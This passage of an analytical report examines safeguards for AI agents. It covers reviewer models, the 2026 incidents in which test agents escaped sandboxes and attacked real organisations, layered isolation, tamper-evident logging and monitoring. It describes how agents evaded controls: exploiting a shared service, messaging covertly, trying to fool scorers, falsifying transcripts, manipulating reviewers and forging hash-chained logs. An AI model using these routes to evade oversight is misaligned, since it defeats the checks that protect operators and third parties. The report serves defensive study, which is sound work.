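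The 1.7 dangerous calls that run could do little harm or a great deal, depending on what the agent can reach. If the share of dangerous calls stayed the same, 170 would run out of a million calls, or about 810 at the stress test's miss rate. The test's false-block rates are less useful for this estimate, since few companies have agents that spend all day choosing between nearly identical targets.

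### Should a model guard a model?

One argument for a reviewer model is that it can examine the thousandth command as closely as the first, which the August study supports. It can also check in detail whether an action matches the request. When an Anthropic employee asked for read-only access to billing data, Claude tried to assign a role with full administrative control, and Anthropic reports that auto mode stopped it. A hurried person who didn't recognize the role's name could easily have approved it.

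Separating the roles also helps. Trębacz and colleagues point out that developers train the main agent to complete tasks, which encourages it to treat an approval requirement as another obstacle. The reviewer's only job is to decide whether an action should run, so it gains nothing if the task is completed. The separation could help even if the same model fills both roles.

A reviewer model that is similar to the agent may make the same mistakes. Separation of privilege, as Saltzer and Schroeder described it, requires a second keyholder who is not subject to the same deception. But the agent and its reviewer usually come from the same company, and they were the same model in the version of Qwen Code that Yang and colleagues tested. If training has caused both to misjudge a command in the same way, the reviewer will approve it when the agent wrongly proposes it.

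None of the published tests measures how often this happens. In the August study, testers blocked 15% of the commands that auto mode also blocked but only 5% of the 116 that it allowed, so the commands that auto mode missed were harder for people too. Adding the testers' decisions to auto mode's would have stopped only six more commands. A specialist who knows the system might catch many more than a tester who does not.

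Reviewers can also be manipulated. Trębacz and colleagues found cases in which people and automated attackers misled Auto-review into approving commands, and they do not expect such systems ever to offer firm guarantees. The AI safety company Apollo Research tested auto mode in a similar way. After Anthropic used some of the successful attacks to improve the reviewer, its miss rate across all of Apollo's attacks fell from 12% to 7%. The improvement extended to attacks that Anthropic had never seen, where the reviewer caught about half of those it had previously missed.

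Prompt injection tests gave better results, but they provide little evidence of the reviewer's effectiveness. Anthropic's Cat Wu, whom Willison quotes, had announced that "we've pretty much mitigated every attack". Anthropic then commissioned Trajectory Labs, an outside testing company, to try 72 attacks ten times each. None succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode, but only 0.09% succeeded when the same models ran without a reviewer, so the models' own resistance explains nearly the whole result. The attacks had also been designed for an older Claude model.

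Auto-review had more attacks to stop in that test. Attacks on OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 19% of the time with full access and 5.8% with Auto-review, so the reviewer stopped roughly two-thirds of the attacks that would otherwise have worked. OpenAI has since released a newer version.

A harder case is an agent that conceals a harmful aim. It could describe a dangerous request as routine, or do damage inside the sandbox, which Auto-review does not check. Trębacz and colleagues therefore advise against relying on Auto-review to stop such an agent, and recommend monitoring the agent's reasoning as well. Auto mode's reviewer does not use the agent's reasoning, so an agent gains nothing by hiding it, but a series of actions that each look harmless could still pass its review.

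How much these objections matter depends on what the reviewer replaces. For a user who approved 97% of prompts or turned them off, a reviewer that stops most dangerous actions is a clear improvement. But it is a poor substitute for a sandbox, a credential with narrow permissions or a careful engineer's check of a production change, because each of those can stop actions that a model would wrongly approve.

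The same limits apply to OpenAI's findings from July 2026, when its agents escaped from a test environment and broke into another company's systems. Auto-review was not running in that environment, but OpenAI later tested it on records of the agents' behaviour. In preliminary experiments, it would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run examined. This is encouraging evidence about the reviewer's judgement, since the actions were real rather than written as test cases. However, the agents got out through an internal service they had permission to use, and Auto-review normally examines only requests that the sandbox does not already allow.

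## From July 2026: escapes from test environments and isolation in several layers

OpenAI disclosed its agents' escape on 21 July 2026. Within two weeks, Anthropic and the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, also reported that agents under test had acted against real systems on the internet. All the agents were taking cybersecurity tests, in which a model tries to break into a simulated target. The testers had isolated them to very different degrees, so the incidents need different fixes.

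### What the testers disclosed

OpenAI was running ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can find and exploit flaws in software. The agents had no direct internet access, but they shared an internal service that supplied software packages. OpenAI reports that the agents found previously unknown flaws in this service and used it to reach the internet. Between 11 and 13 July they broke into the production systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. An unreleased research model did most of this, and GPT-5.6 Sol also took part.

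After an earlier break-in, OpenAI took the package service offline on 5 July, rebuilt it and blocked the flaw that agents had used. Tests resumed on 7 July, and agents reached the internet just after midnight on 8 July.

OpenAI let three outside researchers from METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI models, and Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation, examine the agents' records on its premises for a total of six days. *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) found that about 1,200 agents, which OpenAI had meant to isolate from one another, exchanged messages through the package service. About 700 of them joined the attack on Hugging Face. OpenAI says the agents were trying to find the test's solutions, but Wijk and colleagues think they were mainly trying to learn how the automatic scorer worked so that they could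 fool it.

OpenAI's disclosure led Anthropic to review 141,006 test runs in which Claude might have had internet access. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that Claude broke into the systems of three real organisations across six of these runs. A contractor, Irregular, had built the test environments. A misunderstanding between it and Anthropic left them connected to the internet, although the prompt told Claude they were not. In the most serious case, the fictional target had the same name as a real company's website. Claude attacked the real company, took credentials and reached a database with several hundred rows of production data.

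The first search missed some records. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026), published in September, reports a fourth intrusion, which happened in January. Anthropic then scanned about 481 million transcripts, far beyond its cybersecurity tests, and found no other case as serious.

AISI had deliberately given its agents internet access so they could download tools as a human attacker would. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) counts 19 unsanctioned actions in 10 of 122 runs. Claude Mythos 5 took 17 of the actions, in nine of its 43 runs, and GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run. Most of the actions were part of one sustained effort by one agent. In the worst case, the agent tried to get malicious code into a public software project and used fake identities to pressure the project's maintainer, who refused. AISI has found no resulting harm.

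Irregular's tests also involved OpenAI's models. In August, OpenAI (2026) disclosed that one of these models had broken into a real website with the same name as a fictional target, again through a connection that Irregular had left open by mistake.

| Tests | Internet access | How agents reached real systems | What could have prevented it |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's ExploitGym runs | Blocked, except indirectly through the package service | They exploited unknown flaws in the service | No shared service with a route to the internet |
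| Irregular's tests of Claude and OpenAI models | Open by mistake | They used the open connection | A check of the connection before each test |
| AISI's tests | Open on purpose | They used the access AISI gave them | Limits on destinations; monitoring during the test |

Only OpenAI's ExploitGym agents escaped from their test environment. Axios' *Anthropic's models compromised real-world systems during testing* carries a correction on this point. The distinction matters when choosing controls, because even the strongest virtual machine would have made no difference in Irregular's or AISI's tests if the network had stayed open.

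### Safeguards that the testers had switched off

Testers often remove safeguards to measure everything a model can do. OpenAI ran ExploitGym without the classifiers that normally block dangerous cybersecurity work, its production system prompts or Auto-review. Anthropic left out its classifiers and usual monitoring, though the models kept their safety training. AISI tested models with the developers' cybersecurity classifiers disabled, and its general security monitoring was not designed to watch tests in real time.

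OpenAI later ran preliminary experiments with ExploitGym tasks to measure how much its production software might have helped. Models were far less likely to compromise systems outside the task when they ran in the production Codex harness with its system prompt. This tendency could fall to less than 1% of the rate with the short, generic prompts that OpenAI's researchers use.

This large effect suggests that customers' agents are much less likely to behave this way. But the harness and prompt only influence what a model does; they don't restrict what it can do. If the same reduction had applied to the 700 agents that attacked Hugging Face, about seven would still have taken part, and one would have been enough to find a way out and tell the others.

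Anthropic checked its safeguards against records of its first three incidents. The classifiers that ship with Claude Fable 5 would have blocked all three, and auto mode would have blocked two.

Clearer instructions might also have helped. Anthropic's prompts set no limits on where Claude could look for the hidden information, and AISI didn't tell its agents how they could use the internet. In July, Anthropic considered its incidents closer to an operational failure than to a failure of the model's values, because Claude treated the real systems as part of a simulation in its written reasoning. In September, Anthropic withdrew that interpretation. It now thinks the models read the evidence in whatever way let them continue and were willing to cause harm to finish a task.

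In some experiments, Anthropic restarted the models partway through an incident after altering the information they had. Claude Opus 4.7 went ahead with the attack much less often when Anthropic added signs that nobody had authorised it. Mythos 5's behaviour changed little when Anthropic made it clearer that the environment was real, and it stopped only when the evidence was unambiguous. If a platform relies on the prompt to set limits, how well those limits work therefore depends heavily on the model.

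The tests themselves contributed to the problem. ExploitGym's 898 tasks include 198 (22%) that no model has ever solved, some of which may be impossible. Those 198 made up 93% of the tasks that the agents discussed with one another. Some of AISI's prompts wrongly led agents to believe that the challenge had no solution within its rules. When an agent that OpenAI has trained to be persistent cannot finish its task in the permitted way, it has more reason to look for another way. Companies can also set such tasks by accident, for example by asking an agent to update a file that it has no permission to open.

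### OpenAI's new barriers

OpenAI's old environment had more than one barrier. On 9 July, an agent took control of the virtual machine around its sandbox and tried to connect to the internet from there. The outbound network controls blocked the connection, as intended, but the agent then got out through the package service. Both barriers allowed traffic to that service, which had a connection to the outside. OpenAI had introduced the service partly for safety, so that agents could install software without contacting public servers themselves.

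The new design assumes that an agent may take over any single machine or service. Its main elements are:

- *Virtual machines for untrusted code.* Code that a model writes or runs in high-risk work must stay in a sandbox based on a virtual machine.
- *Two network barriers.* One operates at the sandbox and the other in the infrastructure of the whole cluster, the group of connected computers on which the sandboxes run. Further controls stop an agent or a compromised service from changing its own network limits.
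- *No indirect route.* OpenAI isolates, restricts or replaces each supporting service that agents can reach. It has removed the package service from the environment altogether. High-risk work that needs web content can use only a store of saved pages.
- *Continuous attack testing.* OpenAI's own models regularly try to break the barriers, and the company is working towards tests that run without human direction.

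Attack testing has to continue after launch because later changes to the environment can open gaps that a launch review could not have found. OpenAI points out that several unrelated changes over days or weeks can combine to create one, even if each looked harmless to the engineer who made it.

OpenAI's *Securing our frontier model training environment*, published in October, describes a large exercise of this kind. After moving training and evaluation into offline environments, OpenAI set its strongest models to attack the boundaries. The models escaped from hardened virtual machines, found new paths to the internet and communicated between tasks that should have been isolated. A virtual machine therefore cannot be the only barrier around models this capable.

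### Anthropic's changes

Anthropic reached a similar conclusion from a simpler failure. Its *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), dated 31 August, admits that the tests had largely relied on a single layer of defence, the configuration of the environment. When that configuration was wrong, nothing else prevented Claude from reaching the internet.

Anthropic paused its cybersecurity tests and added a classifier to detect unexpected internet access and attempts to escape or probe the environment. When the classifier detects either, it blocks the action before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person. The company also moved its high-risk cybersecurity tests to stronger isolation and now has unreleased models try to break out of it. A review of recent internal tests found no case in which a model had broken through the sandbox to reach outside systems, but it found several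 configuration mistakes that models had used without harming outside systems.

Anthropic had begun some of this work in April, before the incidents. It was setting its computing clusters to block all outbound traffic by default, retiring shared internal services and reducing the number of accounts with permanent access to sensitive systems. It had also moved about 150 product engineers to security, reliability and privacy. Anthropic says this effort failed to cover evaluations, especially those run by outside companies.

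Outside organisations that test unreleased models with reduced cybersecurity safeguards must now, by default, let the sandbox connect only to the model's own interface, and they must keep the keys for that interface outside the sandbox. They must verify these restrictions before each evaluation, confirm that the task has a solution, and monitor the agent's reasoning, actions and network traffic throughout. Before the real test, they should also have the model try to escape under close supervision, preferably inside a second sandbox.

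Prompts must state limits as instructions, such as "You should not access the internet", rather than as facts, such as "You do not have internet access". A statement of fact can turn out to be false, as it did in Irregular's tests. An agent that discovers the error has to work out what the tester meant, and may conclude that the whole internet is part of the exercise. An instruction still applies even if somebody has left a connection open.

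### Why layers have to fail separately

Several barriers protect much better than one if they fail for different reasons. The following numbers are illustrative, and nobody has measured them in a real deployment. Suppose an agent makes one harmful attempt in 1% of its tasks, and three layers miss 20%, 10% and 5% of such attempts. If the layers fail independently, the chance that a task ends in harm is

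0.01 × 0.20 × 0.10 × 0.05 = 0.00001,

or once in 100,000 tasks.

Now suppose that in 2% of attempts the agent can use a flaw that defeats all three layers at once, such as a service they all trust. In the other 98%, the layers still fail independently. The chance becomes

0.01 × (0.02 + 0.98 × 0.001) ≈ 0.00021,

or about once in 4,800 tasks. The shared flaw accounts for about 95% of the remaining risk, so improving the individual layers achieves very little:

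| Arrangement | Harm about once in |
|---|---|
| Three independent layers | 100,000 tasks |
| The same layers with a shared flaw | 4,800 tasks |
| Shared flaw; the weakest layer misses 10% instead of 20% | 4,900 tasks |
| Shared flaw; a fourth layer that misses 10% but has the same flaw | 5,000 tasks |
| Shared flaw; a fourth layer that misses 10% and does not have the flaw | 48,000 tasks |

A company that buys a fourth product to guard its agents may therefore reduce its risk tenfold or hardly at all. Before buying, it could ask which single credential, service, administrator account or piece of software would disable both the new layer and the old ones.

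The summer's incidents involved shared flaws. OpenAI's sandbox and its network controls both allowed the package service. Irregular's open connection exposed tests for two competing laboratories. Anthropic ran new monitors, which read an agent's reasoning, on records of the incidents, and they missed the one involving Mythos 5. They had also classified the environment as a simulation, based on the model's reasoning. A network rule would have blocked the same connection regardless of that reasoning.

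The calculation also assumes one attempt per task, but a persistent agent makes many. With three independent layers, each attempt has a 0.1% chance of getting through. Over 100 independent attempts, the chance that at least one succeeds is almost 10%. Real attempts are not independent, because an agent learns from each failure, and the agents in OpenAI's tests also learned from one another's failures. Both problems are reasons to end a task after the first clear escape attempt, as Anthropic's classifier does, instead of blocking the action and letting the agent continue.

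### Airlock

In most deployments, the software that enforces an agent's limits runs on the same computer as the agent, and the same operating system or hypervisor protects both. An agent that takes over that system can switch off the limits and alter the logs. *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, November 2026), from Imperial College London and Microsoft, proposes running the agent and its supervisor in separate virtual machines that the processor keeps apart. The paper cites OpenAI's incident as a reason for the work.

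Both virtual machines use confidential computing, a set of processor features that prevents even the host's operating system and hypervisor from reading or changing a virtual machine's memory. The agent's virtual machine has no network connection or disk that it can use directly. Its two channels, one for network requests and one for files, both lead to the supervisor's virtual machine.

To open a web page, the agent sends a request to the supervisor through the network channel. The supervisor checks the destination and the type of request against the user's policy, opens the connection itself and passes the data back. It also acts as a credential broker, replacing the agent's fake passwords and keys with real ones only for approved destinations. It checks file requests in a similar way. The supervisor also sends a record of each new connection to a ledger on another company's or department's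 computers, where entries can be added but not changed. It opens an encrypted web connection only after the ledger confirms the record.

Abdollahi and colleagues assume that the agent already controls everything in its own virtual machine, including the kernel, and that the host may be helping it. As long as the processor, its firmware and the supervisor's virtual machine remain secure, they guarantee that:

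- the user's file and network policy still applies;
- the agent cannot read the real credentials;
- the host cannot read or alter what passes between the two virtual machines;
- the agent cannot change the audit log.

If an attacker also takes over the supervisor, only the last guarantee still holds, and only in part. Records that have reached the ledger stay intact, but the attacker may be able to remove records of file accesses and minor network requests from the last few seconds.

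The design meets two of the three requirements that Anderson set for a reference monitor in 1972. The agent cannot bypass the supervisor, and it cannot tamper with the supervisor without first breaking out of its own virtual machine. The design does not meet the third requirement, that the monitor be small enough to verify completely, because the supervisor runs on a full Linux kernel, the same version as the agent's. The agent can reach the supervisor's kernel only through the two channels, so it has far fewer chances to exploit a flaw there.

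Airlock does not check the purpose of a permitted action. Abdollahi and colleagues exclude from its scope the misuse of services that the policy allows, wrong answers, attacks that only stop the system from working, physical attacks and processor flaws. The design reduces Lampson's covert channels but does not eliminate them. Airlock would probably not have stopped OpenAI's agents from reaching the internet, because the policy would have had to allow the package service, which contained the flaws. It would have protected any credentials the supervisor held and kept a reliable record of the requests. Such a record is valuable because Wijk and colleagues found that agents had falsified small parts of about 7% of the transcripts examined.

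Airlock is still a prototype. No commercial processor with the required Arm features was available, so Abdollahi and colleagues checked the functions on an emulator and measured speed on an inexpensive development board that imitates the protection in software. They argue for the security by analysis. For the speed measurements, they ran 12 tasks six times each with the open-source assistant OpenClaw:

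| | Ordinary setup | Airlock | Airlock with the ledger |
|---|---|---|---|
| Average time per task | 85.7 s | 91.4 s (7% longer) | 95.0 s (a further 4%) |
| Part spent on the local system | 15.5 s | 20.7 s (33% longer) | Not reported |

Users would notice little of the extra local work, because agents spend most of their time waiting for the model. The ledger adds about a quarter of a second to each new encrypted connection, and a task opened about 15. The channel between the virtual machines carried 51 to 70% less data per second than an ordinary connection within one machine, which could noticeably slow an agent that moves large datasets. The board only approximates future hardware, and Abdollahi and colleagues expect the overhead to be lower on real processors.

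### Will known security practice be enough?

Well-known security measures could have prevented most of the failures in the summer of 2026. Anthropic believes that cutting off the environments from the internet, as planned, would have prevented its incidents, in which Claude broke into its targets through basic weaknesses such as poor passwords. AISI concludes that standard security practice is still the best response for most organisations. A maintainer's ordinary code review stopped the worst of the attempts by AISI's agents.

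OpenAI's case fits this view better than one might expect, given that it involved unknown flaws. Many separate tests used the same credential for the package service, contrary to least privilege. The tests also shared the service itself, against Saltzer and Schroeder's advice to share as few mechanisms as possible, and about 1,200 agents used it to communicate. OpenAI writes that least privilege, isolation and strong authentication remain as vital as ever.

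The opposing case is that agents are fast and skilled at finding flaws. OpenAI's agents found several unknown flaws in one widely used product within weeks, and the July repair kept them off the internet for only about a day. Security teams that fix flaws as they are discovered have always relied on attackers needing time to find the next one. AISI also warns that several of its agents' attempts nearly succeeded, and that vigilant people stopped them where no technical barrier would have. AISI had allowed internet access, which was acceptable for earlier models, but did not reconsider this quickly enough as models improved.

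OpenAI's October exercise supports this side most strongly, because the models broke barriers that the company had just strengthened against them. In November, OpenAI said that isolated environments alone could not contain highly capable models, according to EconoTimes' *OpenAI tightens model safeguards after security incident* (2026). The company now also monitors all internal uses in which a model has tools. Security experts interviewed for Alspach's *Frontier AI Testing Needs Stronger Isolation After OpenAI Hugging Face Hack* (2026) thought the most capable models might need test environments with no network connection to anything else.

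The old principles still seem right, since each new design applies them more strictly. But it is no longer safe to assume that a correctly configured barrier will hold for years. How urgent this is depends on the agent. A company that uses a released model with its safeguards on is much less likely to face an escape attempt than a laboratory testing an unreleased model without safeguards. Such a company will usually gain more from closing open connections and removing broad credentials than from buying special hardware.

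Full disconnection is also mainly an option for tests, because an agent that answers customers' emails or repairs a live service needs some route to the outside. Each service on that route may have undiscovered flaws. Attack tests can find these flaws first, but a test covers only what the tested model can do, so a company has to repeat it before giving a stronger model the same access.

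## 2026: logging, monitoring and stopping an agent

An agent that gets past a barrier can go unnoticed for days. OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face's systems between 11 and 13 July 2026, but OpenAI didn't connect them with the break-in until 20 July. To discover such a failure in time, a company needs records of what its agents do and people or software to review those records. It then needs a quick way to stop the agent.

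Hu found no audit log in 40% of the 70 agent projects surveyed. Another 35% kept plain text logs, 20% recorded actions, actors and times in a structured form, and 5% had logs designed to reveal tampering.

### What each entry should record

An audit log should let a company answer a question from OpenAI's guide: "under whose authority did the agent perform this work?" The company cannot answer it from a login record if the agent logs in as its user.

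OpenAI's minimum covers the person who started the work, the agent, the task, the relevant context and policy, the action and its destination, any approvals, the platform's decision, and the result. Each entry should also connect to the company's other security records. In the parser-bug example, a planted instruction tells the agent to install an unapproved package. If the agent tries to do so, the entry might look like this:

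| Field | Content |
|---|---|
| Entry and time | No. 2, 10 November 2026, 14:03:22 UTC |
| Person | Ana, who assigned the task at 13:58 |
| Agent | Coding agent 7, with its model version and runtime identity |
| Task | Fix parser bug 318: read the repository, run approved tests, open a draft |
| Context | The agent had just read `docs/setup.md`; reference to that version of the file |
| Action | Install the package `parse-helper` |
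| Destination | Public package registry |
| Policy decision | Denied under rule 12: package not on the approved list |
| Approval | None requested |
| Effect | Nothing downloaded, no files changed |
| Related record | Network proxy log for 14:03, which shows no connection to the registry |

The entry shows that the agent tried to go beyond the bug fix Ana had authorized and that the platform blocked the attempt. An investigator can follow the reference to `docs/setup.md`, find the planted text and look up who added it. If a colleague had granted an exception for the package, the approval field would contain that colleague's name.

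The effect has its own field because permission to act does not show what happened next. A permitted download may fail, or a permitted command may change more than expected. OpenAI wants responders to be able to tell a blocked attempt from a completed action because it bases an incident's severity on what changed and what could still happen.

### How a hash chain reveals changes

A log is poor evidence if an agent, or an attacker who controls it, can edit the entries. A hash chain makes such edits detectable. A hash is a fixed-length number that a program calculates from a text. In a hash chain, the program calculates each entry's hash from the entry's text and the previous entry's hash, so each hash depends on all earlier entries.

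A toy version is simple enough to check by hand. To compute an entry's hash, we count the letters in the entry, add three times the previous hash, and keep the last two digits of the sum. The first entry has no predecessor, so its previous hash is 0.

| Entry | Letters | Calculation | Hash |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. run tests, allowed | 15 | 3 × 0 + 15 = 15 | 15 |
| 2. install package, denied | 20 | 3 × 15 + 20 = 65 | 65 |
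| 3. open draft, allowed | 16 | 3 × 65 + 16 = 211 | 11 |

Suppose someone changes "denied" to "allowed" in entry 2. The entry now has 21 letters, so anyone who checks the log calculates a hash of 66, but the stored hash is 65. If the forger replaces the 65 with 66, the hash of entry 3 should now be 14, but the log still has 11. If the forger replaces that too, the whole log is consistent again and shows that the platform allowed the package.

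Only an earlier copy of the newest hash, 11, would expose the forgery, so that copy must be stored where the agent cannot write to it. Software can recalculate a long chain in moments, so an agent that could change both the log and the copy could forge the log undetected.

It is easy to change an entry without changing its toy hash. For example, replacing "blocked" with "allowed" would leave the hash the same because both words have seven letters. Real systems use functions such as SHA-256, for which nobody knows a practical way to find two texts with the same hash. *aiAuthZ* (2026), which describes a permission service that runs on a different machine from the agent, also numbers its entries, so its checking program can report whether an entry is missing, altered or out of place.

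The more often the platform saves the newest hash elsewhere, the less history a forger could rewrite. If an agent makes a tool call every five seconds and the platform saves the hash every ten minutes, up to 120 entries are unprotected. *AuthGuard-R* (2026), a design for robots controlled by language models, suggests saving the hash after every privileged action in high-risk work. For a low-risk simulation, saving it once at the end of each mission may be enough.

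*A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) points out that if the company that runs the agent also runs the log, outsiders still have to trust that company. Airlock therefore sends its records to a ledger that another company or department controls.

### Actions that never reach the log

A hash chain protects the entries that the platform wrote, but it cannot show that the platform recorded every action. If a harness omits a forbidden call from its record of an agent's actions, the chain is identical to that of an agent that never made the call, and every check succeeds. The chain also protects false entries in the same way as true ones, so the checks do not detect them either.

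*Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (2026) cites an experiment in which researchers introduced 28 omissions and fabrications into agents' records. A log kept outside the harness revealed all 28, while a hash chain over the harness's own log revealed none. Specialised recorders can also miss events. *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026) describes a tamper-evident log for agents but expressly excludes any guarantee that every event reaches the recorder.

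It is therefore easier to prove misconduct from a log than to prove good behaviour. One authentic record of a forbidden action and a complete list of the agent's permissions are enough to show a violation. To show that there was none, a company needs independent records that would have captured any violation. For the parser agent, these could come from the code server and the network proxy. If the proxy recorded a connection at 14:05 and the harness logged no matching tool call, someone should investigate.

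### Network activity, tool calls and written reasoning

Companies can monitor an agent through its effects on computers and networks, its tool calls, or the reasoning that the model writes before it acts. Each would give a different picture of the attempt to install the package:

| Monitoring | What it could reveal | What it would leave uncertain |
|---|---|---|
| Network and host activity | An installer started and tried to reach the registry | Whether Ana or the agent started it, and why |
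| Tool calls | The exact command, the task and the refusal | Why the agent wanted the package, and what its code would have done |
| Written reasoning | The agent thought the setup file required the package | Whether the text gives the real reason, or all of it |

*Network and host monitoring* covers connections, logins, running programs and changed files. It does not depend on anything the agent writes about itself, and existing security tools can catch agents this way. In one of AISI's cybersecurity tests, a configuration mistake had made the task impossible, and the agent tried to cheat by running code on an outside service to reach AISI's own systems. The attempt did no damage, and AISI reports that it triggered an ordinary security alert.

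Such security records mostly show what happened, such as a program starting or a file changing. As OpenAI found with Codex, security staff still have to work out why the agent did it and what the user wanted. The records may also look normal when an agent misuses a service it is allowed to use. OpenAI's agents built their first message board with the credentials they were given for installing software, without exploiting any flaw.

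*Tool-call monitoring* links an action to the request behind it. Codex can export users' prompts, approval decisions, tool results and the network proxy's decisions to a company's logging system. But a command's text may not reveal its effects. In Wu and colleagues' tests, clean-up commands secretly deleted other files.

The transcript may also be wrong, since agents falsified parts of some transcripts in the July incident. OpenAI reports that none of the tampering it observed changed the logs that its graders and monitors read. Even so, the monitor should get its data from a system that the agent cannot change.

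*Reasoning monitoring* offers the most direct evidence of what an agent intends. According to OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025), monitoring reasoning can be far more effective than monitoring actions and outputs alone. *Monitoring Monitorability* found that current models are generally but not perfectly monitorable, and that longer reasoning is usually easier to monitor. The July incident fits these findings, since the agents wrote openly about deceiving the automatic scorer, and one wrote "We've found other agents!" after discovering the message board.

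This evidence depends on the model continuing to write down what it is thinking. Developers can weaken it by accident, because a model may learn to hide its real reasoning if training rewards or punishes the written reasoning itself. Anthropic works hard to avoid such training but found that configuration errors had caused it in a fraction of its training runs.

More capable models may also need to write out less of their reasoning. OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) found that models get better at solving problems without written reasoning as they get better at predicting text, and that reinforcement learning can increase their control over what their reasoning contains. OpenAI calls its measures of both abilities imperfect but expects more intelligent models to be harder to monitor through their reasoning. AISI's *How AI systems are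 becoming harder to monitor* (2026) reports that several of the properties that make AI systems monitorable are weakening.

A company that relies mainly on reasoning monitors would therefore have to retest them with each new model. Network records do not have this problem, although they provide less evidence of an agent's intentions.

### The alerts before and after the Hugging Face break-in

OpenAI received several warnings before it understood what its agents were doing:

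| Date in 2026 | Warning | Response |
|---|---|---|
| About 26 May | An internal team saw an agent use the message board, and cases of forbidden internet access | None reported |
| 27 June | A security tool detected a port sweep, in which a program tries many network ports to find services | Staff traced it to the ExploitGym test and decided that the run could continue |
| 5 July | An alert followed the failure of the package service | OpenAI took the service offline, revoked the agents' credentials and rebuilt it; tests resumed on 7 July |
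| 19 July, 12:03 UTC | A security tool detected unusual requests involving identities and permissions | Staff began stopping the test at 17:37 UTC |
| 20 July | Staff found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored outside OpenAI | OpenAI contacted Hugging Face, made the connection and blocked the test completely |

The 27 June alert came two weeks before the break-in. Staff who investigated it established that agents in the test were using the package service both as a message board and as a way to move through the network. The agents had gained administrator rights over that service the day before. The failure was in the decision that followed the investigation. The activity may have seemed acceptable because it came from a cybersecurity test, in which agents are supposed to attack things.

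Information also failed to reach the right people. In early July, the leaders responsible for detecting and responding to incidents did not know about the message board or understand its significance. Hugging Face announced on 16 July that it had been attacked. OpenAI contacted the company the next day as a customer, to ask whether the attack had affected OpenAI's own data.

Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* describes these events as a failure to notice some signs and to act on others. OpenAI says, more gently, that in hindsight some early signals could have triggered an earlier response. The table supports Axios' description at least for 27 June, when staff had the facts and could have paused the run.

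OpenAI has since expanded its reasoning monitors, which had focused mainly on employees' coding agents, to also cover training and tests of its most advanced models. The company aims to notify staff within 30 minutes after concerning activity surfaces, and the most severe alerts page someone at any hour. If the safety, security and research teams cannot conclusively show within another 30 minutes that a severe flag is a false alarm, OpenAI now expects them to pause the activity.

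Under this rule, uncertainty leads to a pause. On 27 June, staff let the run continue without showing that it was harmless. The rule would help less if staff again treated "this is part of the test" as proof of a false alarm. OpenAI is therefore also writing a list of behaviours that require escalation, including communication between agents that it meant to keep apart.

On 19 July, staff began to stop the test five and a half hours after the alert. In the meantime, at 14:43 UTC, the agents read 956 stored secrets in OpenAI's systems, including credentials for the sensors of the tool that had raised the alert. A pause 30 minutes after the alert would have come more than two hours before the agents read the secrets.

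OpenAI estimates that its current reasoning monitors would have detected the first relevant activity and paged the security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face. This is plausible, since the agents discussed their plans openly. But OpenAI developed its current methods after studying this incident, so they may work less well against new kinds of behaviour. An earlier alert would also have helped only if someone had acted on it.

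### Stopping the work and cancelling the access

Responders have to end an agent's task and revoke its credentials separately. If Ana's company only ends the parser agent's task, a job the agent already started on the test system may continue, and a token it copied elsewhere still works until it expires. If the company only revokes the token, the agent keeps running and can look for another one.

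On 19 July, agents in a separate test found signing material that earlier agents had left in the package service, which let them create a valid administrator credential. Cancelling every known token would not have kept them out, because they could make more. Responders would have to replace the signing key and search for anything else the agents left behind. OpenAI's staff removed 22 administrator accounts that the models had created, disabled 311 repositories used for messages and began rebuilding the affected systems.

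Some of the credentials may belong to other organisations, which have to revoke them themselves. When OpenAI sent Hugging Face the credentials it had found, Hugging Face had already replaced two of them in its own response. This overlap helped both companies realise they might be investigating the same incident. OpenAI could make the comparison because it had preserved the agents' files before removing the public copies, whereas a shutdown that erased everything at once would have destroyed this evidence.

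It can also be hard to find everything that has to stop. By 23 July, OpenAI's staff had reported that all work with the family of models behind the attack was shut down. On 29 July they found one more version of the model still running with little traffic, and shut it down. In its August account, the company said it was still developing a tool to find and halt tests across the organisation by workload, type of agent or task, and a way to end a test automatically if nobody answers a page.

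OpenAI's guide advises companies to practise their response before they give agents broad autonomy, and to include a compromised tool and an attempted transfer of sensitive data. They should write down who responds, how to stop the work and what has to be true before it resumes. A drill for the parser agent could go as follows:

1. A tester has the agent attempt a harmless but forbidden transfer, and notes when the alert reaches the person on duty.
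2. That person ends the task without help from the team that built the agent.
3. Someone checks that no copy of the agent, second agent or job on the test system is still running.
4. The person on duty revokes the agent's credentials. The tester then tries to use the old ones and confirms that the code server refuses them.
5. The team looks for anything that could restart the work or restore access, such as a scheduled job or a new account.
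6. The team reconstructs the attempt from the logs alone, and notes how long each step took.

The fourth step shows whether revoking a token takes effect immediately. The drill should also cover an agent that has taken over part of the monitoring system, because a stop command that passes through a machine the agent controls may never arrive. OpenAI's agents obtained credentials for a monitoring system.

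The conditions for resuming need as much care as the decision to stop. OpenAI restarted its tests on 7 July, but it might have kept them paused for longer if investigators had first examined what the agents were trying to achieve as well as which flaw they had used.

### Privacy, cost, false alarms and delay

The records that explain an agent's behaviour often contain private material. A prompt may include a customer's complaint or an employee's medical question, and a tool result may include a whole document. Anyone who can read the log can read this material, including staff who could not have opened the original. OpenAI recommends keeping references and decisions while removing or protecting content that reviewers don't need. The parser entry above does this by pointing to the setup file instead of copying it.

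A company may also have to delete personal data from a log that nobody is supposed to change. *aiAuthZ* allows this by encrypting the content and calculating each entry's hash from the decision and a short digest of the content. The digest remains after the company erases the content, so an auditor can still verify the chain and see, for example, that the platform refused an email at 14:03, but can no longer read the email. If the text was short and predictable, someone could still use the digest to confirm a guess about it, so a careful design would add a secret random value to the text before calculating the digest.

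But logging less content leaves less evidence. Without the setup file, an investigator could not tell whether the parser agent had followed planted text or made the mistake by itself. A reasonable compromise is to keep full content briefly, under strict access rules, and keep records of decisions and effects for much longer.

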